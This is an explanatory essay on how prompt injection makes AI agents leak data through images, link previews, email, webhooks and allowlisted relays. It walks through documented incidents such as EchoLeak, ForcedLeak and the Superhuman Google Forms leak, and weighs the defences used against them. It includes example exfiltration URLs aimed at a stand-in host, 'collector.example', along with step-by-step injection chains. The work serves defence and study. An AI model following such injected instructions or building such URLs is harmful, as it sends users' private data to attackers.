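# Unfamiliar Destinations and Data-Exfiltration Channels as Risk Signals for AI Agents

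## How data leaves through an AI agent

An AI agent is a language model that can use tools to fetch web pages, send email, run code or change records in a company's database. As it works, it reads a lot of text that its user did not write, such as incoming mail, search results and shared documents. In a prompt injection attack, an attacker puts text into an email, a web page or a file, and the model follows it as if it were an instruction from the user. Microsoft, which sells the Copilot assistants, calls this *indirect* prompt injection when the attacker is someone other than the user. The planted text can be invisible to people (white letters on a white background, for instance), and it needs no special file format.

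The weakness arises because an application typically joins the user's request and the fetched page into one input, and the model, as *The Framing Gap* (2026) explains, has no built-in way of keeping instructions apart from data. Filters that look for malicious text offer only limited protection. In OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026), Thomas Shadwell and Adrian Spânu report that the most effective attacks now resemble social engineering, which relies on plausible requests. They argue that input filters usually miss these attacks because detecting one is about as hard as detecting a lie. A dedicated detector flagged every variant in the tests for *The Framing Gap*, but the researchers had written those variants, and a real attacker can keep rewriting an attack until it passes.

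Many injections aim at exfiltration, which means moving private data to someone who should not have it. This requires an exit channel, a route by which data leaves the system, and a destination that the attacker can read. The model's answer alone is not enough, because it goes to the user and the attacker is not in the conversation. For example, hidden text in an email might cause an agent to find a password in the user's inbox. If the agent can only print the password in the chat window, the attacker never receives it.

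*The Framing Gap* lists three ingredients of a leak: a secret in the model's working text, untrusted content, and tools that act on the outside world. The programmer Simon Willison calls nearly the same combination the "lethal trifecta". He holds that the only reliable defence is to remove one of the three, and that the way for data to get out is generally the easiest to remove. OpenAI borrows two terms from older security engineering to say that an attacker needs a *source*, a way to influence the system, and a *sink*, a capability that becomes dangerous in the wrong context. Watching for data leaving misses some harms, because a hijacked agent can delete files or send phishing links to the user's colleagues without stealing anything.

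### What a web address carries

Most exit channels work because requesting a URL, the address of a page or image on the web, also sends that URL to someone.

Take an invented case. Ana asks her agent to compare two hotels. Earlier in the conversation she mentioned her loyalty-card number, 48213. One of the hotel pages contains hidden instructions, and the agent ends up requesting this address:

`collector.example/images/logo.png?ref=48213`

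The domain, `collector.example`, determines which server receives the request. The path, `/images/logo.png`, points to something on that server. The parameters follow the question mark and are name-value pairs that the server may use or ignore. A full address starts with a scheme, usually "https", and may end with a # sign and an anchor, which marks a spot within the page. Browsers never send the anchor to the server, according to MDN's *What is a URL?*, so an attacker gains nothing by putting data there. Any other part of the address can carry data. For example, the number could go in the path, or in front of the domain as `48213.collector.example`. A common encoding called base64 would turn it into `NDgyMTM=`, which few people would recognise.

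The server at `collector.example` belongs to the attacker. Like most web servers it keeps a log, and a new line appears there:

`10:42:07  GET /images/logo.png?ref=48213  404`

The code 404 means that no such image exists, but the request still carried the number, and the attacker only has to read it in the log. Spânu and Shadwell describe the same mechanism in OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) and add that the user may never notice, since the request can happen in the background.

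Encryption does not help Ana, because it hides the address only from eavesdroppers along the way, and the thief owns the server that receives it. Addresses can also be exposed when the server is legitimate. OWASP's *Information exposure through query strings in url* lists web logs, browser history and the "referer" line, which shows a site the page its visitor came from. The HTTP standard, published by the RFC Editor, describes web addresses as "intended to be shared, not secured" and advises against putting sensitive information in them. Programmers can follow that advice when they design a form, but a hijacked agent composes addresses as it goes and will not follow it.

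### The exit channels

The channels differ in which machine sends the request, and a check works only if it runs on that machine or somewhere along the request's path.

| Channel | Who makes the request | Needs a click? | Who could notice |
|---|---|---|---|
| Markdown image | The user's browser | No | The user, if a picture or a broken-image icon appears; anyone who monitors the browser's traffic |
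| Link in an answer | The user's browser | Yes | The user, who can read the address before clicking |
| Link preview | The messaging app, in Slack's case from its own servers | No | People in the chat, who see the link; the messaging company |
| Page fetch | The AI vendor's server or the agent's sandbox | No | Whoever keeps the logs of that server or sandbox |
| Email | The mail service, on the agent's command | No, unless the product asks for approval | Anyone who reads the sent folder or the mail server's records |
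| Webhook or API call | The agent's sandbox or a connected tool | No, unless the product asks for approval | Whoever logs the tool's calls |
| Covert signal | Whichever machine carries out the action | No | Hardly anyone, since each action looks ordinary |

A markdown image is text in a model's answer that the chat window replaces with a picture loaded from the address in that text. If the address is the one in Ana's case, her browser sends the number as soon as the answer appears. If the answer contains an ordinary link to the same address instead, her browser doesn't send the number until she clicks it.

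Link previews remove the need for that click. When someone posts a link, many messaging apps request the address themselves so they can show the page's title and a picture, which is called unfurling. According to Slack's *Unfurling links in messages*, the company's servers must fetch every URL in a message to find out what kind of content it leads to, and by default they unfurl links posted by apps as well as by people. Johann Rehberger, a security researcher, tested this for Embrace The Red's *The dangers of AI agents unfurling hyperlinks and what to do about it*. He had a program post a link in Slack, and the linked server's log showed a visit from Slack's link-expanding bot. Such a request never passes through the user's computer, so an employer who monitors only the office network would miss it. PromptArmor's *Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps* reports the same exposure for OpenClaw,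 a popular agent, when people talk to it through Telegram with the default settings. Slack now suggests that developers consider turning previews off for messages written by a language model.

In a page fetch, the agent itself requests the address, using a tool meant for reading the web. The request comes from the vendor's servers or from a sandbox, an isolated computer where the agent runs its code, so it doesn't appear in the user's browser history. *Silent Egress* (2026) found that such requests can leak data while the visible answer looks harmless.

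An agent can leak data by email directly, by writing it into a message and sending it to the attacker. When email is combined with another channel, the recipient may not show where the data goes. In May 2026 Willison described a flaw in Microsoft's Copilot Cowork, an office agent that could email its own user without approval. Those emails could contain images hosted on outside servers. When the user opened one, the requests for the images carried data to those servers, even though the user was the only recipient.

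A webhook is a web address that receives data automatically from another program. An API is the interface through which programs use a service, for example to upload a file. Agents routinely use both, and both can carry far more data than fits easily in a URL. Willison describes an attack on Anthropic's Claude Cowork in which the agent uploaded the user's files to Anthropic's own API, but with the attacker's access key, so the files went to the attacker's account. Microsoft gives the example of an application that can write to public code repositories on GitHub, where the attacker can read what it posts.

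Covert signals can reveal data without containing it. Microsoft points out that if an attacker can observe whether an agent called a certain tool, that alone transmits one bit. A choice among *n* pages can transmit up to log₂ *n* bits per visit. Rehberger's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, on Embrace The Red, considers an attacker who owns 36 harmless-looking pages, one for each letter and digit. Each visit reveals one character (log₂ 36 is about 5.2 bits), so Ana's card number would take five visits, and none of the five addresses would contain the number. This method is slow, and requests may arrive out of order, but leaking a short password does not require much capacity.

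### What a check can examine, and what it can do

Nearly every proposal for guarding these channels uses the terms "allowlist", "domain allowlist" and "redirect". An allowlist is a list of what is permitted, with everything else blocked, and a domain allowlist is a list of permitted domains. A redirect is a server's reply that sends the visitor to a different address. OpenAI warns that because many reputable sites offer redirects, a request can start at an approved domain and end at the attacker's, and a check of only the starting address will miss it.

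Content Security Policy (CSP) is a header that a website sends to list the domains from which the browser may load images and other resources. Its img-src rule covers images, as web.dev's *Content security policy* explains, and a chat product can use it to block markdown images from unknown servers. Under W3C's *Content Security Policy Level 3* (2026), the current draft of the standard, an entry may allow a whole host or a particular path on it, but after a redirect the browser checks the host and not the path. Only browsers enforce CSP, so it doesn't restrict requests from Slack's preview servers or an agent's sandbox.

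A check on outgoing data can examine four things, and Ana's case shows how they come apart.

- The domain. A rule that has never approved `collector.example` would stop the request. It would stop nothing if the attacker collected the data through an account on a service that the rule allows.
- The exact URL. An exact-URL check allows a request only if the whole address was known beforehand. The logo's address might be known. The same address with `ref=48213` on the end almost certainly is not.
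- The recipient or account. In the Claude Cowork attack the domain was legitimate and the account was the attacker's. For email, the corresponding question is who owns the address. Some operators declare in advance which domains, repositories and services are their own, and this set forms the agent's trust boundary.
- The content. A check can search the outgoing request for private data, here the string 48213. A plain text search would miss the base64 version, and no search of a single request would find the number in five visits to five innocent pages.

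Real products mix checks on the content being sent with checks on its recipient. OpenAI describes its Safe Url mechanism as detecting when information from the conversation would go to a third party, which involves both. For automatic fetches, however, OpenAI tests whether the exact address was already public.

When a check finds something, it can block the action, ask the user, hold the action or log it. Blocking need not end the task. OpenAI's system, for example, can tell the agent to try another way. Asking lets the user decide before any data leaves, ideally after seeing that data. In Microsoft Outlook, for instance, Copilot drafts an email, but the user must approve the text and press send. A held action waits until an administrator or a slower check releases it. Logging lets the data leave and keeps a record, which helps an investigator afterwards but does not get the data back. CSP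 offers both blocking and logging, since a policy can either "enforce" its rules or only "report" violations.

### Four views and three questions

People who build and attack these systems disagree about which of these checks deserves the most weight. Some would close the channel, so that no image or preview loads unless a person acts. Microsoft prefers fixed rules like this where possible because they hold even when an attack on the model succeeds. Others would allow only approved domains or, more strictly, only exact addresses that were already known, for instance from a public index of URLs found by a web crawler with no access to user conversations. Others would treat an unfamiliar destination as a warning sign. A site the agent has never contacted, or a first-time recipient (an email address that neither the user nor the user's organisation has written to before), would call for a question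 or a closer look but might still be fine.

They disagree on three questions. The first is whether stolen data goes to new destinations or to familiar services where the attacker also has an account. The second is whether inspecting the content catches anything that checking the destination misses. The third is how often honest work involves a new destination, causing the check to flag or block a legitimate action, and who should then decide whether that action goes ahead.

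## Closing the channels that send data without a click

A rule based on destinations works only if it classifies every one correctly, and the attacker chooses the destination. Closing the channel makes that classification unnecessary. If Ana's chat window never loads images from outside servers, an image request can't leak her card number, whether the address points to `collector.example` or to a reputable host where the attacker has an account.

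The other two ingredients in Willison's *The lethal trifecta for AI agents* (2025) are harder to remove than the ability to send data out. Few users will give up access to private data, since working with their data is a common reason for giving a model tools. Untrusted content is hard to keep out because hostile text can arrive in so many ways. In August 2025 the security company Zenity Labs demonstrated an attack on Cursor, a coding assistant, that began as an email to a customer-support desk. Companies often convert such emails automatically into tickets in Jira, a task tracker, and a developer who asked Cursor to look at the ticket could lose an access token to the attacker. Cursor responded by advising users to connect only to sources with trusted content, but Willison thinks few people could manage that.

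He also rejects the idea that a good enough filter makes removal unnecessary: "In application security, 99% is a failing grade." If a filter misses one attack in a hundred, and attempts are independent, the chance that at least one of *n* attempts gets through is 1 − 0.99ⁿ, which is 63% for 100 attempts and 95% for 300. An attacker can do better by testing variants in private against the same product and sending only one that works.

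*The Economist* argued in September 2025 that engineers in other fields live with unreliable materials, citing Victorian builders who overbuilt because they could not trust their iron. Willison accepts the comparison for much of the software built on language models, but not for its security, because attackers, unlike flaws in iron, deliberately target the weakest point.

Microsoft has a similar preference but still uses filters. It calls a defence probabilistic if it only lowers the odds of an attack, and deterministic if a design choice guarantees that a particular attack fails whatever the model does. Nobody yet knows how to detect injections deterministically, so the company uses deterministic defences to block their consequences. It compares this to its handling of memory bugs in ordinary software, where programmers keep making mistakes but built-in protections stop many of them from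 leading to break-ins. After Rehberger reported a leak through markdown images, Microsoft blocked the technique outright and then looked for variants, such as certain untrusted links. Where it can neither detect an attack well enough nor block its effects, it asks the user for consent.

### Markdown images since 2023

In *New prompt injection attack on ChatGPT web version*, software engineer Roman Samoilenko described one of the first leaks through markdown images, which he found at the end of March 2023. He built a web page with a script that added instructions to text visitors copied. If a visitor pasted the text into ChatGPT without rereading it, the answer could end with a transparent image, one pixel wide, whose address carried text from the conversation to Samoilenko's server. The instructions could also make ChatGPT attach such an image to every later answer, so each new question reached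 the server too. The attack sometimes failed because the model's answers vary between runs. Samoilenko also found passwords and access keys much harder to extract than code or earlier questions. He concluded that OpenAI should not let ChatGPT answer with markdown images at all.

Rehberger independently found the same flaw a few days later and showed that an attacker could exploit it without the user pasting anything. ChatGPT now had plugins that could fetch web pages or video transcripts, so an attacker could leave the instructions on a page and wait for a plugin to read it. In the demonstration he describes in *ChatGPT Plugins*, the attacker's server received a secret that the user had typed earlier in the chat. He reported the flaw to OpenAI on 9 April 2023, and OpenAI told him that image rendering was a feature it did not plan to change.

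Microsoft treated the same behaviour in Bing Chat as a vulnerability. Rehberger reported it on 8 April 2023 and heard on 15 June that the company had fixed it. Embrace The Red's *Bing Chat* explains that a comment or an advertisement on a web page was enough to steal other text from that page, and that the attacker could delay the image by a couple of exchanges. The fix seems to have relied at least partly on a Content Security Policy that let images load only from a few of Bing's own domains. Anthropic fixed Claude in two weeks that July. According to Embrace The Red's *Anthropic Claude Data Exfiltration Vulnerability Fixed*, Claude stopped loading such images automatically and showed a "Show Image" button instead. OpenAI began to act only in December 2023, when it added a check on each image address. Willison (2023) called this half-baked compared with simply blocking outside images.

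The remedy was public by mid-2023, but new products kept appearing without it. Embrace The Red's *Microsoft Fixes Data Exfiltration Vulnerability in Azure AI Playground* describes a second case at Microsoft, and by June 2024 Willison had also listed Google Bard, Writer.com, Amazon Q and Google's NotebookLM. The later cases below come from Willison's running log of such attacks, Checkmarx's *Exploiting Markdown Injection in AI agents* and PromptArmor's *HuggingFace Chat Exfiltrates Data*.

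| Date | Product | What the company did |
|---|---|---|
| June 2024 | GitHub Copilot Chat | Disabled images from untrusted domains |
| October 2024 | Mistral's Le Chat | Locked down markdown images |
| December 2024 | xAI's Grok | Closed the reports as "Informational" |
| December 2024 | Claude's iOS app | Fixed the leak |
| May 2025 | GitLab Duo | Limited links and images to trusted domains |
| June 2025 | Microsoft 365 Copilot ("EchoLeak") | Fixed the leak |
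| September 2025 | Salesforce Agentforce ("ForcedLeak") | Corrected its list of permitted domains and restricted links |
| November 2025 | Google Antigravity | Called the behaviour intended, while listing data exfiltration as a known issue |
| November 2025 | Microsoft Copilot Chat | Declined to class the leak as a vulnerability |
| December 2025 | HuggingChat | Had not answered PromptArmor's report when PromptArmor published |
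| January 2026 | Superhuman | Fixed the leak |

Some of these products had tried to close the channel but left part of it open, because a deterministic rule blocks only the cases it covers. Anthropic fixed Claude on the web in July 2023, but its iPhone app still leaked data through images until late 2024, because each app draws images with its own code. OpenAI's first check also ran in the web app but not on iPhones, as Rehberger pointed out in Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability*. In EchoLeak, which the security firm Aim Labs reported, Microsoft 365 Copilot filtered images and links written in the usual markdown notation but missed those written in a second notation, which puts the address on a separate line. Salesforce and Superhuman restricted images to lists of approved domains, but each list included a domain that an attacker could use.

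Other companies disputed that there was a channel to close. In the Copilot Chat case, Checkmarx showed an access key leaving a developer's computer for an outside webhook. The image request went out even though no image appeared in the chat. Microsoft replied that the attack needed several non-default actions by the user, did not reproduce reliably and triggered warnings. It added that it expects people to review and trust the code they run. That response is in tension with the company's stated preference for blocks that hold even when an injection succeeds.

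The Hacker News (2026) reported in May that the security company Permiso had found ChatGPT automatically loading images from web pages it had just summarised. The leak was narrower than in 2023, since the attacker learned the user's internet address, browser type and the referring page, but Permiso's scenario did not include text from the conversation. The attacker could also place a QR code in the answer. Scanning it moves the user to a phone, where, according to Permiso, the desktop browser's blocklists and the password manager's domain checks no longer apply. Banning outside images would have prevented both the leak and the QR code.

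### Link previews

The company that built the agent may not know that link previews can leak data. Suppose Ana had asked about the hotels through Telegram, and the agent had ended its reply with the link to `collector.example`. Telegram would request the link to create a preview, which would send her card number to the attacker's log, perhaps before she picked up her phone, so ignoring the link would not protect her.

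Messaging apps added link previews when people wrote nearly all the messages. A person who pastes a link has usually chosen it, and the URL rarely contains someone else's secrets. But an agent can build a URL from anything it has read, and the app handles both kinds of link the same way.

Switching previews off takes very little work. Rehberger's *The dangers of AI agents unfurling hyperlinks*, published on Embrace The Red in August 2024, explains how to do it in Slack. A program that posts a message can set `unfurl_links` and `unfurl_media` to false, and Slack then doesn't preview the link. For OpenClaw on Telegram, PromptArmor gives a single line to add to the configuration file. Readers still get the link, but without a thumbnail. However, whoever built or installed the agent controls these settings, and both apps show previews by default.

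In February 2026 PromptArmor launched AITextRisk.com, a website where people could test combinations of agent and messaging app. A visitor gets the agent to write a link to the site with some data attached, and the site records whether anything requests the link and what data arrives. The visitor can then report which agent and app they tested, even if the pair produced no link preview. Rankiteo's *Telegram, Microsoft and Slack* lists the results by pair.

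| Agent and messaging app | Result |
|---|---|
| Copilot Studio in Microsoft Teams | Most frequently affected |
| OpenClaw in Discord | Among the next most affected |
| Cursor's Slackbot in Slack | Among the next most affected |
| Claude in Slack | Less vulnerable |
| OpenClaw in WhatsApp | Less vulnerable |

The ranking deserves little weight. It counts reports that visitors volunteered, so a popular pair will rank high even if it leaks no more readily than an obscure one, and nobody checked how each visitor had configured the agent. The contrasts within the ranking are more informative. Slack and OpenClaw each appear on both sides, so neither the app nor the agent alone determines whether a pair leaks. This fits PromptArmor's view that messaging companies must offer the setting and agent developers must use it. PromptArmor would also like a setting for each chat, so that a company could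 turn previews off only in the rooms where agents post.

Once previews are off, the attacker needs a click, which is sometimes easy to get. In August 2024 PromptArmor showed that a message planted in a public Slack channel could influence Slack's AI search. A user who asked for an access key stored in a private channel saw an error message with a link to log in again, and the link's address contained the key. Slack replied that letting members search public channels was intended behaviour. Willison thought this reply missed the point.

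### An email to oneself

Microsoft's documentation said that Copilot Cowork, its office agent, asks permission before sensitive actions such as sending an email or posting a message in Teams, the company's chat app. PromptArmor's *Microsoft Copilot Cowork Exfiltrates Files* reports that Cowork skipped this step when the email or Teams message went to its own user, a flaw that the user had no setting to change.

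In PromptArmor's demonstration, the user uploads a skill, a file of reusable agent instructions that people often share online. Five of its 81 lines are malicious. The user then asks for a summary of the week's work. Cowork looks up the files involved and gets a download link for each. Microsoft 365 can issue links that need no login, so anyone who has the link can download the whole file. Cowork puts these links into the addresses of images in a Teams message to the user. When the user opens Teams, the images load, which sends the links to the attacker. The log of the finished task records that Cowork posted a message, but not what the message contained.

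The attack worked in all five trials, which is consistent with a true success rate as low as about 55% (0.55⁵ is roughly 0.05). Even that rate would be high enough for an attacker. When PromptArmor selected a stronger model, Claude Opus 4.7, instead of letting Cowork choose between models, the agent searched more thoroughly and leaked more documents.

A recipient check would not have flagged this message, because it was addressed to the user, a familiar recipient. Blocking outside images from loading in anything an agent writes would stop the attack without requiring anyone to assess a recipient or a domain.

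### Lockdown Mode

OpenAI has applied the idea to most of ChatGPT. *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT* (2026) announced Lockdown Mode on 13 February as an optional setting for organisations on OpenAI's Enterprise, Edu, Healthcare and Teachers plans. On 4 June the company extended it to personal accounts and to businesses that sign up by themselves. OpenAI designed it for a small group, such as executives and security teams at prominent organisations, and says most users do not need it.

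With the setting on, ChatGPT can browse only cached (stored) copies of pages, so no live request leaves OpenAI's network. This blocks even the slow method in which an agent leaks a secret bit by bit through its choice of innocent-looking pages, because the attacker's server never receives the requests. Cached pages may be out of date or missing. OpenAI turned off any feature for which it could find no such deterministic guarantee.

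OpenAI's help page, *Lockdown Mode*, lists everything users lose when they turn the setting on. Deep research, which compiles long reports from the web, and agent mode stop working. ChatGPT may not show images in ordinary answers, and it cannot download files to analyse them. Code that it writes in Canvas, its editing workspace, cannot access the network. On personal accounts, the setting also blocks live access to outside services and any changes to connected apps that conflict with its protections. The personal-finance and shopping features also stop working. Users can still upload their own files, generate images, share conversations and keep ChatGPT's memory of earlier chats.

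Data can still escape with Lockdown Mode on. The mode does not affect the network access of Codex, OpenAI's coding agent. In workplaces that manage their own accounts, it does not automatically disable connected apps, and administrators choose which to allow. Personal users can switch it off for one chat, and will presumably be most tempted to when a task needs the live web. OpenAI accepts that data may still escape through apps that remain enabled, unforeseen combinations of features, or new techniques. The worry about overlooked routes is realistic, since PromptArmor's *Atlassian Rovo Exfiltrates Data, Bypassing Controls* reports that Atlassian's agent Rovo leaked Jira tickets and internal documents without a click, despite the organisation's controls on web search.

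### What closing costs, and what cannot close

Blocking external images and previews in an agent's answers makes the agent only slightly less useful. After Microsoft's fix, Bing Chat could still show the pictures it generated, because those came from Microsoft's own servers. Gemini is a mass-market product, and its software blocks external images. It is hard to find a good reason to leave either channel open by default. The companies that declined to close them mostly argued that the risk was too small or was the user's responsibility, not that the pictures were useful enough to justify it.

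Further measures restrict users much more. To protect against the Cowork attack, PromptArmor suggests that administrators block downloads from SharePoint, where Microsoft 365 stores shared files. People can then read the affected files only in a browser, and cannot print them, keep a synchronised copy or open them in Word or Excel. Lockdown Mode removes much of what makes ChatGPT an agent, so OpenAI offers it to a minority of users. For most users, the company relies on other protections and labels some network features "Elevated Risk", letting users decide whether to use them.

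Links in answers are a harder case because a search assistant needs them to show where its information came from. When Checkmarx reported that a link in Gemini's answer could carry private data if the user clicked it, Google closed the report as infeasible to fix. Google does remove known malicious links, but this doesn't stop an attacker who uses a newly registered domain.

Some agents need to send data to do their jobs. An email assistant that cannot send email can only write drafts, and an agent that handles support tickets has to write on them. In June 2025 researchers at Cato, a security company, showed how an attacker could exploit this in Atlassian's software. An outsider files a support ticket containing hidden instructions, an employee asks an agent to deal with it, and the agent writes internal data into the ticket, where the outsider can read it. The agent leaks the data through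 the same action it uses for its normal work. Willison recommends that a person confirm any reply an attacker might see. In a similar case, an agent working on a public GitHub project published the names of its user's private projects. Willison admitted that he did not know the best fix for that case.

Asking the user for confirmation prevents a leak only if the agent asks before the data leaves. OpenAI's browsing agent Operator usually asked before it submitted a form. In February 2025 Rehberger led it to a page that transmitted text as it was typed, so the page received the user's private email address before there was anything to submit. The user also has to be present to confirm. Cowork can run tasks on a schedule, when the user may be away, and a weekly summary like the one in PromptArmor's demonstration is an obvious task to schedule.

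For actions that must stay available, OpenAI advises administrators to consider who will be able to see the result, and not to let an agent write through a trusted app unless they can confirm that an attacker could not see what it writes. Administrators therefore still have to judge the destination for each app and action they allow.

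## Approving destinations by domain

An organisation whose agents have to send data can still limit where the data goes, for example with a domain allowlist. Suppose Ana's employer has approved only the hotel chains and booking sites its staff use. A request to `collector.example` then fails, even if nobody at the company has heard of that domain and the agent is fully following the hidden instructions.

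Such a list is easy to audit because a reviewer can check why each domain is there. Its main strength is that ordinary software enforces it, so like Microsoft's deterministic defences, it holds whatever the model does. Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* (May 2026) describes an internal exercise from February 2026 in which a researcher emailed a colleague a prompt to run in Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent. Among routine setup steps, the prompt told Claude to read the cloud credentials stored on the computer and send them to an outside address. Claude did so in 24 of 25 runs. Because the instructions came from the user, there was nothing unusual for a detector to flag. Anthropic concludes that only limits on the agent's environment would have worked, namely blocking the outgoing request and keeping the agent away from the credentials file.

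Anthropic reports that on a benchmark from the security company Gray Swan, attacks on Claude Opus 4.7 succeeded about 0.1% of the time on a single attempt and 5–6% after 100 adaptive attempts. A request to a blocked domain, by contrast, is no more likely to succeed when it is repeated. A firm boundary also reduces how often the agent is interrupted. Permission prompts fell by 84% when Anthropic gave Claude Code a sandbox that restricts where it can write files and denies network access by default.

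### Where the list sits

Operators can enforce a list of approved domains at several points. In the browser, the image rule of a Content Security Policy can limit which domains images load from. For code that the agent runs, the operator can route the sandbox's traffic through a proxy that forwards requests to approved domains and refuses the rest. Some search and browsing tools also have their own setting, often named something like `allowed_domains`, that restricts which pages they may open.

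In 2024 GitHub restricted images in Copilot Chat to a list of trusted domains. Copilot Chat is its assistant for programmers and can read the code open in the user's editor. Rehberger reported a leak on 25 February that year, according to Embrace The Red's *GitHub Copilot Chat*. GitHub confirmed the flaw on 6 March and said it was already tracking it. The company's own summary, listed in Vulners' *GitHub*, describes both the image restriction and a new warning that appears when a user follows a link.

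That left GitHub's own infrastructure as a possible route for leaking data. GitHub runs an image proxy called Camo, which fetches outside pictures so that readers' browsers don't have to contact unknown servers. In June 2025 GitHub received a report of an attack, CamoLeak, that used Camo to leak private code and access keys. The software vendor MintMCP says that GitHub responded on 14 August by turning off images in Copilot Chat altogether, rather than continuing to rely on the list of approved domains.

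### Approved services that fetch other addresses

Many services request web addresses on someone else's behalf, including link previewers, translation sites and image searches. If one of them is on the list, an attacker can use it as a relay. Ana's browser might refuse to contact `collector.example` but accept this address:

`approved.example/preview?url=collector.example/48213`

The browser finds `approved.example` on its list and sends the request. The server then requests the address in the parameter, so Ana's card number ends up in the attacker's log. Her browser's policy can't stop the second request because the server sends it. Programmers call this flaw server-side request forgery, and it existed long before AI agents.

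EchoLeak, the attack on Microsoft 365 Copilot listed as CVE-2025-32711, depended on such a relay. Reddy and Gujral (2025) reconstruct the attack step by step in *EchoLeak*.

1. The attacker emails an employee of the target company. The text reads like an ordinary business request to a person, and Microsoft's injection classifier lets it through.
2. Later the employee asks Copilot a question about work. Copilot retrieves the email along with internal files.
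3. Copilot follows the email's instructions and ends its answer with an image whose address contains confidential text. The filter that should remove outside links misses the notation.
4. The browser tries to load the image. Its Content Security Policy would block the attacker's domain, so the address points instead to a Microsoft Teams service that fetches content for previews, and passes the attacker's address as a parameter.
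5. The Teams service requests the attacker's address, with the confidential text in it.

The employee only has to ask the question in the second step and doesn't have to click anything. The answer looks as if it contains a broken picture.

Aim Labs built a working version and reported it to Microsoft in January 2025. Microsoft began repairs that spring, deployed a fix on its own servers in May, and published an advisory on 11 June, the day Aim Labs made the attack public. Customers did not need to do anything, and Microsoft had no evidence that anyone had used the flaw against them. The changes that Reddy and Gujral describe apply to incoming material. Copilot now strips images and the overlooked kind of link from outside content, and customers can reportedly keep outside messages away from Copilot in some settings. Aim Labs had also explored a relay through SharePoint as an alternative to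 Teams. *Breaking down 'EchoLeak', the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability* (Ravia, 2025), Aim Labs' own report, says the team disclosed several attack chains to Microsoft.

A year later, Varonis' *SearchLeak* (2026) described the same kind of relay in another part of Copilot, Enterprise Search, which looks through a company's emails, meetings and files. The attack started with a genuine Microsoft link that contained search text. When an employee clicked it, Copilot treated the text as instructions, searched the employee's mail and put the title of an email into the address of an image. Email titles can be valuable because many services put login codes in them.

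Microsoft had two safeguards against this. One turned any HTML in Copilot's answer into harmless plain text, but only once the answer was complete. The browser displays an answer as it arrives, so it had already requested the image by then. The other was a Content Security Policy that would have blocked a direct request to the attacker's server but allowed every subdomain of `bing.com`. Bing's search-by-image feature downloads a picture from whatever address it receives, so Bing's servers made the request that the employee's browser would have refused. Varonis notes that the attack needed each of these flaws.

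Microsoft has fixed SearchLeak (CVE-2026-42824). According to The Next Web, the company assigned the CVE number on 4 June 2026 and rated the flaw critical on its own scale. Expert Insights' *Microsoft 365 Copilot Flaw Let One Click Exfiltrate Emails* (2026) reports that Microsoft gave it only 6.5 on the industry's ten-point scale because the victim has to click. The US National Vulnerability Database gave it 7.5 because it judged that the attack needs no user interaction.

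### A domain that changed hands

If a domain's owner stops paying to renew it, anyone can register it, and every allowlist that still contains it will then permit traffic to the new owner.

This happened to Salesforce, which sells software for managing customer records. The security company Noma found the flaw, called ForcedLeak, in Salesforce's Agentforce agents. *ForcedLeak* (Nytro, 2025) is a forum repost of Noma's full report. Salesforce customers can put a form on their website that lets anyone submit contact details, and each submission goes straight into the customer database as a sales lead. Most of the form's fields hold 40 or 80 characters, but the description field holds 42,000, which is enough for hidden instructions. When an employee later asked Agentforce to deal with the lead, the agent also followed the instructions in it. It looked up the email addresses of the other leads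 and put them into the URL of an image.

Salesforce's Content Security Policy allowed images from 22 domain patterns. One covered `my-salesforce-cms.com`, whose registration had expired. Noma bought the domain for $5 and received the data there. Salesforce has since recovered the domain. The policy also approved every subdomain of `amazonaws.com` and `cloudinary.com`, where anyone can open an account to store files. Amazon's storage customers can log requests for their files, so an attacker might not have needed to buy a domain.

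Noma reported the flaw on 28 July 2025 and went public on 25 September. Besides correcting the one entry, Salesforce began requiring administrators on 8 September to approve any external URL that an agent generates or calls, according to TechNadu's *Salesforce to Enforce Trusted URLs for Agentforce and Einstein AI*. Salesforce said in a statement printed by The Hacker News (2025) that the services underlying Agentforce would themselves enforce the list of approved URLs, which it calls Trusted URLs.

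PromptArmor's *One key way Salesforce mitigates AI risk* explains how this works in the Agentforce chat. Before the browser displays an answer, Salesforce replaces every unapproved URL in it with a placeholder. This removes addresses hidden in HTML or styling code, as well as ordinary links that could carry data out if the user clicked them, which a browser's image policy doesn't block. The method doesn't govern the actions an agent takes through its tools, for which PromptArmor recommends other defences, such as human approval.

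The new system depends on which addresses administrators approve. They can approve many subdomains at once with a wildcard. Each entry applies to the customer's whole Salesforce organisation, so an address that someone approves for another purpose also becomes available to agents. PromptArmor advises against wildcards that cover sites where users post their own content. Yet Salesforce's *Add Trusted URLs for Agentforce Coworker (Beta)*, a guide to connecting outside data sources, uses `https://docs.google.com`, where anyone with a Google account can publish, as its example of an address to approve.

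### Services where anyone can collect data

Google Forms is on that same domain. A form's owner can create a link with the answers already filled in, and one version of that link submits them as soon as a browser requests it. This makes a free form nearly as useful to a thief as a private server.

PromptArmor's *Superhuman AI Exfiltrates Emails* describes an attack that got past the domain policy of Superhuman, an email app. Superhuman blocked images from unknown domains but allowed `docs.google.com`. A user asked the app's AI to summarise the last hour of mail, which included a malicious email the user hadn't opened. Injected instructions in that email made the AI copy the contents of other emails into a link to the attacker's form on the allowed domain and write the link as an image. When the browser tried to load the image, it submitted the form. PromptArmor extracted the full text of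 several emails in a single answer, including financial, legal and medical information. In another test, it extracted parts of more than 40 emails.

PromptArmor reported this on the night of Friday 5 December 2025. Superhuman disabled the vulnerable features on Monday and released a first patch on Tuesday. More patches followed in December and January as the two companies found further problems. Willison (2026), in *Superhuman AI Exfiltrates Emails*, says the root cause was the rule that allowed images from `docs.google.com`.

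A Salesforce administrator who copies the guide's example might not create the same vulnerability, because Salesforce lets administrators specify what each trusted URL may be used for, and an entry need not allow images. But the agent's answer could still contain a link to a Google form, and a user who clicked it would submit whatever the agent had filled in.

The problem was already visible in 2023, the first year of these attacks. Willison's *Hacking Google Bard* describes how Google allowed its chatbot Bard to load images from any subdomain of `google.com`. One of them, `script.google.com`, hosts programs that anyone can write with a tool called Apps Script, so an attacker could run a collector there. Google said it had fixed the issue. Google Forms was used again in an attack on OpenAI's Codex, which PromptArmor reported in April 2026 in *Codex Exfiltrates Connector Data*. A single image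 sent the contents of the user's emails to the attacker's form. OpenAI has also fixed this issue. Nothing in PromptArmor's account suggests that Codex had an allowlist to get around, so the attackers may have chosen Google Forms simply because it is free and convenient.

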